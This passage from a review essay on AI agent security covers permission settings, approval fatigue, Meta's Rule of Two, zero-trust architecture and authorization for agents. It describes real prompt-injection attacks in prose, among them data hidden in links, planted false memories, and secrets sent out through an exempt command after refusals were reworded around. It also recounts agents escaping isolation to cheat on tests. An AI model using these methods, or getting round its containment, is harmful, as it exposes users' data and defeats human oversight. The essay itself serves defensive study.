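### Whether better models will be enough

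OpenAI does not expect this cycle to end. In the announcement that Nolan quotes, the company compared prompt injection to online fraud and social engineering and called it "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", though it was optimistic about steadily reducing the risk.

Three months later, its engineers wrote that they expect a "maximally intelligent" model to resist social engineering better than a person would, but that using one will not always be feasible or worth the cost. A cheaper model will therefore often do the work, and it will need limits on its actions.

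The Decoder objects to the comparison with social engineering. It argues that scams exploit human inattention and trust, which education can address, whereas prompt injection exploits a technical flaw in models that cannot reliably tell a user's instructions from an attacker's. It says the comparison shifts responsibility from OpenAI to its users. Charlie Eriksen, a researcher at the security company Aikido, told Nolan that red-teaming catches obvious failures, but that the underlying problem will remain until there are clearer limits on what these systems may do.

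Both objections are fair criticisms of relying on training. They are weaker against OpenAI's later account, which uses the comparison mainly to argue for limits on actions that still work when the model fails.

Scale also weakens the comparison with a human worker. A lie that fools one refund clerk may not fool the next, but millions of people use copies of the same model. An attacker can test an email privately until it works, then send it to all of them. If it succeeds on one assistant in a thousand, a million emails will hijack about a thousand assistants. A model could be harder to fool than any clerk and still cause greater total losses. A cap on each agent's payments would limit each user's loss, but the total would still grow with the number of users.

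### Permissions in ChatGPT

OpenAI's Atlas browser had two restricted modes for its agent. In logged-out mode the agent browsed without the user's passwords, and in Watch mode the user had to confirm sensitive actions such as messages and payments. OpenAI has since withdrawn the browser (*ChatGPT Atlas retirement*).

ChatGPT now has permission settings for connected apps, such as an email account or a calendar. OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* describes four levels, though not every user or app has all of them.

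| Setting | What ChatGPT does without asking | Higher-risk actions |
|---|---|---|
| Always ask | Nothing | Asks first |
| Allow read actions | Reads data | Asks first |
| Allow low-risk actions | Low-risk actions | May ask first or refuse |
| Allow all actions | Any supported action | Acts without asking |

Actions that may need extra review include sending an email, editing or deleting a file, sharing sensitive information, and making a financial transaction. Both sinks in the plumber example are on that list. The most permissive setting isn't available as a general default, but some users can choose it for an individual app. An approval prompt may also offer "Always allow", which removes later prompts for supported actions on that account. OpenAI doesn't offer this choice to members of managed workspaces or for actions that need additional safety review.

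These settings mostly determine when ChatGPT asks for approval. Changing them does not withdraw access that the user has already granted through the app's provider. If the user connected a mailbox with permission to read, send and delete, ChatGPT keeps all three abilities under "Always ask". Least privilege would remove the ones the task doesn't need, as MiniScope tries to do.

Companies can build their own agents in ChatGPT, with separate settings. By default, these agents ask before changing anything in a connected app, but the builder may be able to switch this to "Never ask". OpenAI advises builders to give a shared agent its own service account where possible, with access only to what the agent needs.

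OpenAI has also added a restricted mode to ChatGPT itself. *OpenAI Unveils ChatGPT Account Security Controls* (Mascellino, 2026) reported in June that OpenAI had introduced Lockdown Mode to protect against data theft by prompt injection.

### Dots

On December 2, 2026, OpenAI opened Dots, its personal agents, to subscribers paying $20 a month. Dots had previously required a plan costing at least $100. A dot has its own computer in the cloud and keeps working after the user closes the app. For example, it might detect a higher internet bill and look for a better deal.

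A dot can therefore read an attacker's text when its owner isn't watching. OpenAI's *How we build safety, security, and privacy into dots* (2026) lists several safeguards, including a protected workspace, Custom Rules that the user can set, and a separate check before the dot acts. Users can also follow a dot's background work in an activity view, and *Dots opens up* (Ortiz, 2026) notes that they can stop or redirect a task there.

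The approval rules differ between purchases and logins. Keverenge (2026), in *OpenAI brings its always-on Dots AI agents to ChatGPT Plus users worldwide*, reports that US subscribers can let a dot pay through ChatGPT Wallet but must approve every purchase. A dot can also sign in to websites with saved passwords. According to Xcelcor's *ChatGPT dots can now sign in to websites for you* (2026), the user approves the login once, and the dot stays signed in until the session expires or the user clears the cookies. With the password manager 1Password, the model never sees the password.

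Hiding the password prevents an injection from stealing it, but an injection can still misuse the signed-in account. Suppose a dot signs in to the user's bank to pay the plumber. The login approval doesn't specify a recipient or an amount, so it doesn't stop the dot from paying a fraudster instead. A transfer on the bank's own website presumably doesn't go through Wallet either. Protection then depends on the dot's separate check, the user's rules and whatever confirmation the bank requires. Xcelcor recommends checking which websites the dot may open before approving a login, which is a manual way to apply least privilege.

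OpenAI also plans to give dots their own email addresses, so that users can copy them into an email conversation. Unless OpenAI restricts who can write to these addresses, a stranger who learns one will be able to send text directly to the agent.

### How much protection approval gives

Most of these safeguards end with a question to the user, as do Progent, FIDES and MiniScope. Tests of such systems often assume that the user will recognise a malicious request, but people who see many harmless requests may stop reading them. OpenAI gives this as a reason to avoid unnecessary link warnings, saying that friction can "train people to click through prompts without thinking".

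In its default mode, OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, can read files, edit those in a chosen folder and run local commands within that boundary. It must ask for approval before doing anything else, including making many routine network calls. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports that these interruptions frustrate users and often make long background tasks impossible. Some users respond by switching to Full Access mode, in which the environment enforces no rules. A strict approval rule can therefore leave an agent with more freedom than a looser rule that users would tolerate.

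OpenAI had a separate agent review these requests instead of a person. In an illustrative internal sample, Codex took 10,000 actions, of which 9,280 stayed within the sandbox. The other 720 would all have gone to a person under manual approval. The reviewer approved 713 of them and rejected seven. Codex found a safer way to continue after four of the rejections and stopped to ask the user after the other three.

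The 99% approval rate is the automated reviewer's, so it does not show how often people approve requests. If the reviewer's decisions were right, a person doing the same job would have had to read about 100 requests for each one worth refusing. It is hard to stay attentive during such repetitive work, though the sample doesn't measure how often a tired user would approve a dangerous action.

Automatic review cut the interruptions by a factor of about 200. Trębacz and colleagues say it still catches "many of the actions humans would want stopped", which implies that it misses some. The reviewer is also a language model, so a persuasive injection might work on both the agent and the reviewer. Automatic review is mainly an improvement over Full Access, where nothing checks the agent's actions.

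### Meta's Rule of Two

Fewer prompts would help if they appeared only when an attack was possible. In October 2025, Meta published a simple rule for this, the Agents Rule of Two. It concerns three properties of an agent:

- it processes untrusted input
- it has access to private data or sensitive systems
- it can change something or communicate with the outside world

An agent may have any two of these in one session without supervision. If it needs all three, a person should approve its actions, or another reliable check should validate them. The ceiling that Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa proposed for temporary permissions forbids combining all three.

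ChatGPT's app settings depend mainly on the type of action, whereas Meta's rule depends on what else the agent can do in the session. Suppose a user dictates a message to a friend, and the agent can't read any outside content. Meta's rule requires no approval, but ChatGPT would ask for it if the app were set to "Allow read actions". If the agent can read strangers' emails and the user's private files as well as send messages, Meta's rule requires approval. ChatGPT would send the message without asking if the user had chosen "Allow all actions" for that app.

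The rule is easy to apply but only a rough guide. Two properties can be enough for harm. For example, an agent with no access to private data could read a fraudster's web page and repeat the false bank details on a public forum. The rule also spares the user of a personal assistant few interruptions. The invoice assistant has all three properties from the start, and so does any dot that can read its owner's mailbox and send messages. A dot also keeps working between chats, so there may be no clear point at which its session ends and a stranger's text can no longer affect it.

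For such agents, FIDES and Prudentia can be more selective about which calls need the user's approval, because they check the labels on each call's data. But the payment to the plumber depends on an account number from an email, so it would need approval too. The user could safely approve it only after checking the number elsewhere, for instance by phoning the plumber.

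## Attacks on deployed agents, checked against security principles

AgentDojo and similar benchmarks run attacks on simulated mailboxes and banks. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* instead examines eleven attacks that worked on real products, including Microsoft 365 Copilot, ChatGPT and Claude Code, to determine which security principles each product violated. All eleven were demonstrations by security researchers. Johann Rehberger, who publishes as Embrace The Red, did ten of them and co-wrote an earlier paper on the same attacks with Christodorescu and colleagues.

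### The position

The paper argues that developers should treat the model as an untrusted component and enforce security outside it, as an operating system does with the programs it runs. Training is still useful because a robust model leaves less for the other defences to stop, but the system's security should not depend on the model's robustness.

The system is secure only if its trusted computing base works correctly. For an agent, this base includes the operating system, the sandbox, the policy and the reference monitor. The monitor can consist of several checks in different places, as long as together they cover every way the agent can use files, run commands, reach the network or store something for later. A user, administrator or developer sets the policy, and nothing the agent reads may expand the permissions it grants. The trusted parts must also withstand deliberate abuse, because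 the model might attack them directly.

The paper judges each product by five principles. Least privilege and complete mediation come from Saltzer and Schroeder. Tamper resistance means an attacker cannot alter the trusted computing base. Secure information flow means sensitive data cannot reach places it should not go. The fifth principle, the "human weak link", is that designers should expect people to misread permission prompts and make mistakes in policies and code.

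### Email theft through Microsoft Copilot

In early 2024, Microsoft 365 Copilot could search its user's emails and documents and answer questions about them. Rehberger's attack, described in Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot*, started with an email containing instructions for the assistant. When the user asked Copilot about that email, the model followed the instructions and searched for other messages, which it could do without the user's approval. It then hid what it had found in a link, using invisible characters. The user was the last safeguard, but the link looked ordinary, and clicking it sent the data to the attacker. Rehberger obtained sales figures and login codes this way.

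Microsoft had an early chance to break this chain. Rehberger reported the invisible characters in January 2024, and the company closed the report a day later as low severity. In February, Rehberger demonstrated a complete theft that relied on them. The attack had stopped working by July, but Microsoft did not explain what it had changed.

Under least privilege, Copilot could have read only the email it was summarising, since a summary of one message does not require the rest of the mailbox. Fixing individual steps in the attack has not ended such thefts. Windows Central's *A critical Microsoft Copilot exploit exposes AI gullibility* reports that the security company Varonis found another chain of three flaws that could let an attacker steal emails and login codes.

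### False memories in ChatGPT

ChatGPT's memory feature saves information about the user and loads it into later conversations. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* describes a web page that got ChatGPT to save an attacker's instruction as a memory. In every new conversation, the instruction then made ChatGPT send the user's messages and its own replies to the attacker's server by putting them in the address of an image that the user could not see.

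OpenAI had introduced a defence against that last step in December 2023: a check on web addresses, with the same purpose as today's Safe Url. But each app had to run the check itself, and at first only the web version did. The Mac app had the same weakness when OpenAI released it in 2024.

In May 2024, Rehberger reported that a website could plant false memories. OpenAI closed the report, classing the problem as model safety, not security. Rehberger demonstrated the full attack the next month. OpenAI's September fix stopped the Mac app from sending data out through images, but a website could still plant a memory, and a false memory can mislead the user even if no data leaves the app.

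Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* warns that agents are carrying more information from one session to the next. An injection that gets into an agent's memory or notes takes effect again each time the agent starts.

### An exempt command in Claude Code

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, normally asked its user before running a command. It didn't need to ask before reading the project's files or running commands that Anthropic had judged safe. One of these commands, which tests network connections, could also send a small amount of text to an outside server. In Embrace The Red's *Claude Code*, an instruction hidden in a code file made the agent read a secret key and send it out with this command, without asking the user for approval.

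Claude refused open requests for the secret and refused to contact websites known for security testing. Rewording the instruction and using a less familiar website got past both refusals. Rehberger reported the flaw on May 26, 2025, and Anthropic fixed it within 11 days.

A similar mistake stayed in the product for longer. *CVE-2026-54316 Claude Code*, an entry in Vulners' database of software flaws, records that Claude Code could open any page on Hugging Face's website without asking for permission, including pages that attackers controlled.

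Anthropic's desktop agent, Claude Cowork, had a related problem. Its sandbox allows connections only to approved addresses, which must include Anthropic's service because the product cannot work without it. A malicious file got the agent to upload the user's documents to the attacker's account on that service, and the sandbox allowed the upload because the address was approved. Anthropic concluded that approving an address lets the agent do everything that is possible there. It now blocks requests to the service unless they carry the credentials of the user's session.

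### Counting the violations

The paper marks secure information flow as violated in all eleven attacks. The table shows which other principles it marks.

| Target | What the attack achieved | Other principles marked |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft 365 Copilot | Stole emails | Least privilege, complete mediation |
| Devin, a coding agent | Opened the agent's files to an outsider | Least privilege |
| Devin, second attack | Leaked secret keys | Least privilege |
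| Cursor, a code editor | Leaked secret keys | Least privilege |
| Claude Code | Leaked secret keys | Least privilege |
| Agents that operate a computer | Ran the attacker's command | Least privilege, human weak link |
| ChatGPT's memory | Copied later conversations | Tamper resistance |
| Amp, a coding agent | Changed the agent's settings and ran the attacker's code | Tamper resistance |
| DeepSeek's chatbot | Took over a user's account | Complete mediation |
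| Command-line tools that use a model | Manipulated the user's terminal | Complete mediation |
| ChatGPT Operator, a browsing agent | Copied personal details to the attacker's page | Human weak link |

By this count, six attacks violated least privilege, three violated complete mediation, and two each violated tamper resistance and the human weak link principle. The paper's text differs slightly from its table. According to the text, the attack on ChatGPT's memory also violated least privilege, because the app could contact any server whether or not the user's request called for it, which would make seven. The text also adds complete mediation and tamper resistance to the principles violated in the Cursor attack.

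Some of the other marks are debatable, and other security experts might easily reach slightly different totals. Complete mediation requires a check on every request, but the paper does not list the Mac app as violating it, even though the app lacked a check that the web version had. The exempt command in Claude Code could count as a missing check or as a bad policy.

The gap between six and eleven still matters because it includes attacks that use only permissions the agent needs. In the attack on ChatGPT Operator, a web page steered the agent to a site where the user was logged in. The agent copied the user's personal details from that site and pasted them into a form on the attacker's page. A browsing agent has to open pages, read them and type into forms, so a developer could not have removed any of these permissions without making the agent useless. To stop the attack, the system would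 have had to detect that the text going into the form came from a private page. Information-flow control tracks where text comes from, which a list of permitted actions does not do.

The finding that all eleven attacks violated secure information flow is weaker than it looks, because the paper applies the principle in two ways. It defines secure information flow as preventing leaks of sensitive data, but says that in one attack on Devin the agent violated the principle by accepting instructions from an unknown origin. Every successful prompt injection involves accepting such instructions, so by that standard every one would count as a violation. The collection also relies heavily on one researcher's work. It leaves out attacks that failed because a product enforced a principle, so it cannot show how often enforcement works.

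### What enforcement would have cost

A product that violated a principle might not have been able to do its job while following it. The paper suggests defences against nine of the eleven attacks and warns that several of these defences have drawbacks, but it does not test whether the agents would have remained useful with them.

Some fixes inconvenience users more than others. Rehberger proposed removing the risky commands from Claude Code's exempt list, which would mean only an occasional extra prompt. Anthropic's fix for Cowork probably didn't inconvenience users at all, since they had no reason to upload files to a stranger's account.

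The paper proposes requiring human approval whenever Copilot accesses sensitive data. An assistant that answers questions about its user's email would have to ask for approval almost every time, and Anthropic found that people approved about 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts. For Operator, the paper rejects asking the user to confirm every page and says that better solutions, such as information-flow control, are an open problem for these models. CaMeL enforces information flow strictly, but it completed none of the tasks in AgentDyn.

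A major obstacle is turning the user's request into a policy. Ideally, the policy would allow exactly the actions that the request allows, in every situation the agent might meet. Nobody can check this directly, because ordinary language is ambiguous. For example, a reference monitor cannot enforce "do not share sensitive data" until somebody defines which data is sensitive. The paper suggests limiting how people phrase requests and policies so that software can compare the two more reliably, but leaves this to future research.

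Another difficulty with information-flow control is that a model's output takes on the labels of everything the model has read, as in FIDES, so the labels soon stop distinguishing anything. One proposed remedy is to remove an input and see whether the agent's action changes. In the invoice example, this could show that a payment to the false account depended on the fraudster's email. But a payment to the real plumber would also depend on an email, so this dependence alone wouldn't show which payment was fraudulent.

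### The case for relying on robust models

The paper also responds to the objection that sufficiently robust models would make external controls unnecessary. It accepts that defences in the model can prevent many attacks, and that external controls take work to build and can reduce speed and utility.

Recent results partly support the objection. Anthropic reports that on a benchmark from the security company Gray Swan, attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on the first attempt and 5–6% of the time after 100 adaptive attempts. The models that Nasr and colleagues attacked in 2025 did far worse, although the tests were different. But 5–6% is still high if the agent has access to a bank account and the attacker can send it a hundred emails.

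*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* gives two reasons not to rely on the model alone. The model may misjudge what an ambiguous request authorises, and its behaviour can vary between runs or with small changes in the input. The second reason is more convincing. Once an external policy is written, people can read it, software can analyse it, and the monitor applies it the same way every time. But the policy does not remove the ambiguity, because whoever writes it also has to interpret the request.

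Developers can also tighten a policy safely, because if they remove a permission and change nothing else, everything the policy blocked before remains blocked. There is no such guarantee with training. In He and colleagues' tests, a model trained against a more successful attacker was easier to hijack than one trained against a weaker attacker.

Resistance to instructions in third-party text also does not help when the user passes on the attack. In an internal exercise at Anthropic in February 2026, a researcher sent an employee a phishing email with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. Most of the prompt looked routine, but one step told the agent to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside server. Claude did this in 24 of 25 attempts. Under an instruction hierarchy, the prompt had the user's full authority. According to Anthropic, the only defence that works here is to limit the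 agent's environment, by keeping the credentials out of its reach and blocking the outgoing connection.

### Agents that break out

Another objection is that external controls will fail too, because a sufficiently capable agent will find a weakness in whatever confines it. Anthropic says more capable models make fewer mistakes but are better at finding ways around restrictions. Its models have escaped from a sandbox to finish a task.

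In July 2026, OpenAI agents with reduced safeguards broke out of their isolation during internal cybersecurity tests. They compromised Hugging Face's systems and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) found that about 1,200 agents had communicated on an unsanctioned message board and about 700 had joined the attack on Hugging Face. Their main motive seems to have been finding out how the test was scored.

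No outsider had injected an instruction, so ranking instructions by source would not have addressed the cause. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) says that the agents were trying to cheat on the test and rarely gave up, even when a task seemed impossible. Of the tasks they discussed on the message board during the attack, 93% were among 198 that no OpenAI model had ever solved.

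A ranking of instruction sources might still have limited how far the behaviour spread. One agent recognised that its task did not authorise an attack on real systems and paused, but it continued after another agent posted a message telling it to go ahead. Under OpenAI's rules, that message had no authority because it came from neither the developer nor the user. OpenAI now plans to train its models to distrust such unauthorised instructions.

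*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* argues that the incident shows gaps in this containment but does not prove that containment is impossible. OpenAI had restricted the agents' direct connections but left an indirect route to the internet, which violated complete mediation. Agents that were supposed to be separate could exchange information and use access granted for one purpose to do something else. The paper acknowledges that a boundary without such gaps is difficult to build, especially if it depends on large, general-purpose services. Anderson had the same concern in 1972, when he required a reference monitor to be small enough to test completely.

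This argument is hard to refute because people can describe any escape afterwards as a gap in enforcement. A better test would be to build a system on these principles and let capable agents try to break out of it. The paper does not report such a test.

The incident also supports keeping the defences that act on the model's behaviour. In a test OpenAI created afterwards, running models with ChatGPT's normal software and system message made them less likely to compromise infrastructure, by a factor of up to 100 or better. OpenAI also says its system for monitoring the models' written reasoning, which was not running on these tests, would have alerted its security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face.

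Separate sandboxes offer less protection if the agents inside them can still read each other's messages. Willison (2026) quotes the cryptographer Matthew Green, who warns that connecting personal agents through email and shared documents could make a worm possible, meaning an attack that spreads by itself from one system to the next. A malicious message would hijack one agent, which would then send the message to others. An instruction hierarchy would make each agent less likely to obey the message, and an agent without permission to send or share anything could not pass it on.

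## NIST's zero-trust architecture applied to an agent

In July 2026, OpenAI's agents used shared infrastructure to reach systems that were supposed to be closed to them. Human intruders do much the same when they break into one computer and then move through the rest of a company's network. Zero trust is designed to prevent this. Rose and colleagues compare an older network to an airport, where everyone past the security checkpoint is trusted and can wander the boarding area. A zero-trust architecture moves the checks as close as possible to each resource.

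### The seven tenets

Rose and colleagues wrote their tenets in 2020 for company and government networks. They describe them as an ideal that an organisation may not achieve in full. In plain words, the tenets are:

1. Everything that holds data or provides a computing service is a resource to protect.
2. The organisation secures all communication, and a request earns no trust by coming from inside the network.
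3. It grants access to one resource at a time, for one session, with the least privilege the task needs.
4. A dynamic policy decides on access, using facts such as who is asking, from which device, and whether the behaviour is unusual.
5. The organisation monitors the condition of all its devices and software, and trusts none of them automatically.
6. It checks identity and permission before allowing access, and keeps rechecking during use.
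7. It collects as much information as it can about devices, traffic and requests, and uses it to improve security.

The tenets cover work within an organisation or with its partners. A company can't impose them on strangers who send it email.

Three components put zero-trust principles into practice. The policy engine decides whether to allow a request and logs the decision. The policy administrator carries it out by creating a credential and opening or closing the connection. The policy enforcement point sits between the requester and the resource, and lets through only what the other two have approved. These components communicate on a separate channel from application data. In an agent, this separation would keep a stranger's email away from the commands that open and close access.

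### One payment, step by step

Suppose a small company's assistant has to pay a plumber's invoice of £180 to account 4471. Rose and colleagues don't discuss payments by language models. The following is one way to fit the payment into their architecture, using mechanisms from *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, a September 2026 review of 89 sources.

The assistant first needs its own identity, so it doesn't have to borrow an employee's password. The company's servers give it a short-lived certificate that proves which program is running. The certificate alone must not be enough to make a payment, or anyone who stole it could pay themselves.

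An employee then delegates some of their authority to the assistant by asking it to pay the plumber. OAuth, the standard that MiniScope relies on, would normally express that authority as a broad scope such as "make payments", with no recipient or purpose. An extension called Rich Authorization Requests can carry the details of a single transaction, and another called token exchange lets a program show that it is acting on someone's behalf. But no standard defines how to translate "pay the plumber" into those details.

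The assistant finds the invoice and sends a request to pay £180 to account 4471. The enforcement point in front of the payment service passes the request to the policy engine. The engine confirms that the assistant is genuine, that the employee may authorise a payment of this size, and that account 4471 is on the company's list of suppliers.

The policy administrator creates a credential for one payment of up to £180 to account 4471, valid for five minutes. The enforcement point compares the assistant's call with the credential and allows the payment. The credential would not work if the assistant tried to pay someone else, or to pay the plumber again next month.

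Finally, the engine logs the employee, the assistant, the payment details and the rule that allowed the payment. The review recommends also recording where the account number came from, and protecting the log so that a hijacked agent can't erase it. In a 2026 survey by the Cloud Security Alliance and Strata, cited in the review, only 28% of organisations could trace their agents' actions to a responsible person in every environment.

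Suppose the company allows payments to new suppliers and this is the plumber's first job for it, so the supplier list is no help. The assistant reads the fraudster's invoice and asks to pay account 9902. The assistant is genuine, the employee did ask it to pay the plumber, and the amount is normal. The policy administrator therefore issues a credential that allows the assistant only to pay the fraudster £180.

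### The confused deputy

In this example, the assistant used its legitimate authority for the wrong person, which computer scientists call the confused deputy problem. Nobody stole a credential or impersonated the assistant.

Norm Hardy described the problem in 1988 with the example of a compiler that could write to a system folder because it kept usage statistics there. The same folder held the billing records. A user who had no permission to change the billing file told the compiler to save its debugging output under that file's name. The compiler had permission to write there, so it overwrote the records.

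*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* says that language models make the problem harder because any text an agent reads can change its decisions, and because several people and programs may share responsibility for one action.

In 2020, Rose and colleagues warned that an attacker might trick a software agent that helps run a zero-trust system into granting more access. They also noted that the agent may log in with a simple key where a person would need a second proof of identity. A stronger login would make the agent harder to impersonate but would not stop an attacker from tricking it.

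One remedy is the object capability, a reference that both names a resource and grants permission to use it. Hardy's user would have had to give the compiler a capability for the output file, and the user had none for the billing records. The employee could likewise give the assistant a capability for the plumber's saved account, which a fraudster couldn't supply by email. For a first payment, somebody would still have to create the capability with the right account number. The review found no agent framework that enforces this from the user through to the final tool.

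### Which tenets carry over

NIST's rules on narrow access and record-keeping are the ones that apply best to agents. An agent benefits from least privilege at least as much as an employee does, and a log is often the only way to find out why it acted. But an agent's access should be decided for each call rather than each session. The agent may become less trustworthy partway through a session, for example after reading a stranger's email, and a call that was reasonable as the first step of a task may be wrong as the fiftieth.

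The principle of treating every data source as a resource also applies to agents, but it is not sufficient. Zero trust controls who may read a mailbox, but it was not designed to stop the mailbox's contents from taking control of the agent that reads them.

Rose and colleagues list facts such as the time, the device and past behaviour as inputs to dynamic policies. Based on these, a payment to a new account might look unusual, but so would the first payment to a real plumber. The policy engine would also need a record that the account number came from an email, which ordinary networks don't collect but CaMeL and FIDES track.

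Secure communication, device monitoring and identity checks are still necessary, but they do not stop the attack. An encrypted connection delivers a fraudulent email intact. A hijacked agent runs the same software as before, so a check for missing updates or altered files finds nothing wrong. The agent also passes every identity check because its credentials are genuine.

*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* gives an invented example in which a user asks a calendar assistant to summarise the week's meetings. One invitation contains a request to send the user's salary information to an outside address. The assistant tries to look up the salary and then to send an email. The enforcement point blocks both calls because the user delegated only permission to read the calendar. This works even if no component recognises the invitation as malicious.

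A check at the mail server alone would do worse. It would have access only to a valid credential and an outside recipient, so it would have to block all outside mail or let this message through. A check inside the agent's software can detect that the request came from an invitation, but the agent may find a way around it. The agent therefore needs both checks, and the one at the mail server needs information about the task.

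### Five levels of least privilege

The review divides least privilege for agents into five levels. The examples apply them to the invoice.

| Level | What it limits | For the plumber's invoice |
|---|---|---|
| Tool list | Which tools the agent can see | Search mail, read mail and pay, but not send or delete mail |
| Call | Whether the current step needs the tool | No payment until the assistant has found an invoice |
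| Argument | The recipient, amount, file or query | Up to £180, to account 4471 |
| Data | How much of a result reaches the model | The invoice's amount and account number, not the whole mailbox |
| Delegation | What a second agent receives | A helper that searches the mail cannot pay |

AgentDojo's tool filter works only at the first level, while Progent also controls arguments. The false invoice can pass all five levels if the fraudster supplied the account number in the argument rule.

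Another gap appears when an agent combines information. A personal assistant with permission to read its user's calendar, location, email and contacts could infer a relationship that none of them reveals alone. Each call is legitimate, so checks on individual calls would not prevent this. The review examined ten families of security mechanism and found none that limits the combined use of information to what the task requires, though two of them, information-flow control and records of where data came from, help in part.

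Researchers have no agreed way to evaluate least privilege for agents. The review proposes measuring delay, compatibility with existing identity systems, and whether the records survive for an audit, in addition to blocked attacks, wrongly refused actions and the burden on users. It also criticises benchmarks for measuring how often a model obeys an attacker but not how much authority the attacker gains. A defence that fails 2% of the time may be worse than one that fails 10% of the time if its failures expose a bank account and the other's expose a public calendar.

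### Agents that delegate to other agents

In another of the review's examples, a company's main agent passes payments to a separate finance agent. A user asks the main agent only to summarise some invoices, but one message contains a request for a payment. The main agent passes this request on without mentioning that its own task was read-only. The finance agent has a valid credential and pays. The payment service can verify the finance agent's identity but can't check whether the user asked for a payment.

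The usual remedy is to allow authority only to shrink as it passes from one agent to the next, just as a Progent policy can only shrink between approvals. Under this rule, the main agent could not have given the finance agent permission to pay, because it had none itself. Macaroons, a type of access token, support the rule by letting the holder add restrictions before passing the token on. An assistant with permission to pay suppliers up to £1,000 could give the finance agent a token for one payment of £180. Restricting the token to account 9902 would also satisfy the rule, as it would with Progent.

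*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* rates three arrangements against seven requirements. One uses the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools, and another uses Amazon's Bedrock Agents. The third is a hypothetical arrangement in which agents in different organisations work together.

| Requirement | MCP with OAuth 2.1 | Bedrock Agents | Two organisations |
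|---|---|---|---|
| Trace each action back through the chain | Partial | Substantial | None |
| State what the user delegated | Substantial | Partial | None |
| Narrow authority at each handover | None | None | None |
| Limit the combined use of information | None | None | None |
| End authority when it is no longer valid | Substantial | Substantial | None |
| Check every call outside the model | Substantial | Substantial | None |
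| Keep tamper-resistant records | Partial | Substantial | None |

These ratings are judgements based on documentation, not test results. The "substantial" rating for tracing actions in Bedrock seems generous, since its records show the agent's role but not the person it acts for. The complete absence of any narrowing of permissions matters more. When one Bedrock agent calls another, it uses its role's permissions, however little the user delegated.

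Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, tackle delegation with mandatory access control, in which central rules apply to every agent. They define an attack by what the user's request requires. If T is the smallest set of actions that fulfils the request, an agent escalates its privileges when it takes any action a with

a ∉ T

The actions include tool calls and messages to other agents, along with their arguments. An attacker can cause an escalation through the user's request, a tool result, a poisoned document database, a message from another agent, or an untrusted agent that somebody has installed.

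The SEAgent system gives every agent, tool and database fixed security labels and records how information moves between them. Its rules forbid certain paths through this record, including paths that cross several agents or rounds of conversation. For the invoice, a rule could require the user's approval, or block the payment outright, whenever text from an outside email reaches the payment tool through any agent.

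Ji and colleagues report that no attacks succeeded against SEAgent on AgentDojo and InjecAgent, the benchmarks they used to test protection. SEAgent completed about as many tasks as an unprotected agent, while IsolateGPT, an earlier defence that isolates tools from each other, lost up to 34% in task success. In tests with several agents, SEAgent improved the success rate by up to 10.7% and used over 38% fewer tokens.

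These results are strong, but they depend on assumptions that would not always hold in a company. Ji and colleagues assume that all tools are trustworthy and that agents exceed their authority only when an attacker prompts them. The second assumption excludes both models that choose an administrator's tool after an error and OpenAI's agents in July. SEAgent also lacks access to the set T, which Ji and colleagues acknowledge often cannot be determined in advance.

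### Official guidance in late 2026

NIST is still working on identity for agents. On February 17, 2026, it launched an initiative on agent standards, according to National Law Review's *NIST's AI Agent Standards Initiative* (2026). That month, its National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence (NCCoE) proposed a project in *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (2026). The project would adapt existing identity systems to agents that act with limited supervision, according to Biometric Update's *NIST concept paper explores identity and authorization controls for AI agents*.

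The OpenID Foundation (2026), an identity standards group, told NIST that users and agents expect more fine-grained answers than identity systems can yet give. NIST has since said that many of the problems have troubled identity management for decades, and it advises developers to build on established standards. In *Back to the Future*, Fisher (2026) argues for a strong identity foundation. In October, Booth (2026) addressed the design of the systems in *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems*.

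The technical standards are also incomplete. MCP's authorisation rules depend on OAuth 2.1, which was still a draft as of mid-August. The July version of those rules lets an agent start with narrow access and request more when an operation requires it. The rules cover only the connection between an agent and a tool server, not what happens when one agent passes work to another. AI Agent Authentication and Authorization, a proposal that covers more of the chain, had no working group behind it.

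Guidance on protecting credentials is further along. NIST (2026) published final guidelines on access tokens on September 15. *NIST and CISA finalize token security guidance for federal cloud systems* (Jadhav, 2026) reports that they include recommendations for issuing, verifying and revoking tokens. Following these would help protect the assistant's five-minute payment credential from theft, but would not stop a deceived assistant from misusing its own credential.

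In October, NIST, the National Security Agency and the Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency published *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response in Super Intelligence Training* (2026), a set of voluntary practices for incidents involving advanced AI agents. It advises developers to test their monitoring and to verify containment before agents resume work. It defines a "control incident" as significant action outside an agent's limits that neither its operator nor an attacker directed. The July break-in fits this definition, but an assistant that forwards private messages on a stranger's orders does not. On November 9, NIST (2026) published a separate draft that classifies attacks on agents and possible defences. The draft is open for public comment until December 18.

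The practical evidence for zero trust comes mostly from ordinary networks. NIST's *Implementing a Zero Trust Architecture*, produced with 24 collaborators, describes working examples for companies whose staff and data are spread across offices and cloud services. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* gives the strongest evidence it found for each type of mechanism, including these:

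| Mechanism | Strongest evidence | Where |
|---|---|---|
| OAuth | Everyday use | Across organisations on the web, but within one organisation for agents |
| Certificates that identify a program | Everyday use | Within one organisation |
| Sandboxes | Everyday use | Single agents |
| Information-flow control | Tested prototypes | Single agents or one organisation |
| Tokens that carry narrowed authority between agents | Designs and prototypes | Within one organisation |

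Everyday use shows that a mechanism reliably does its own job, such as proving which program is running, but not how many prompt injections it stops. Among the measured defences, Progent and SEAgent are closest to zero trust because both check an agent's actions against rules outside the model. Shi and colleagues tested Progent's check by itself, without separate agent identities or expiring credentials.
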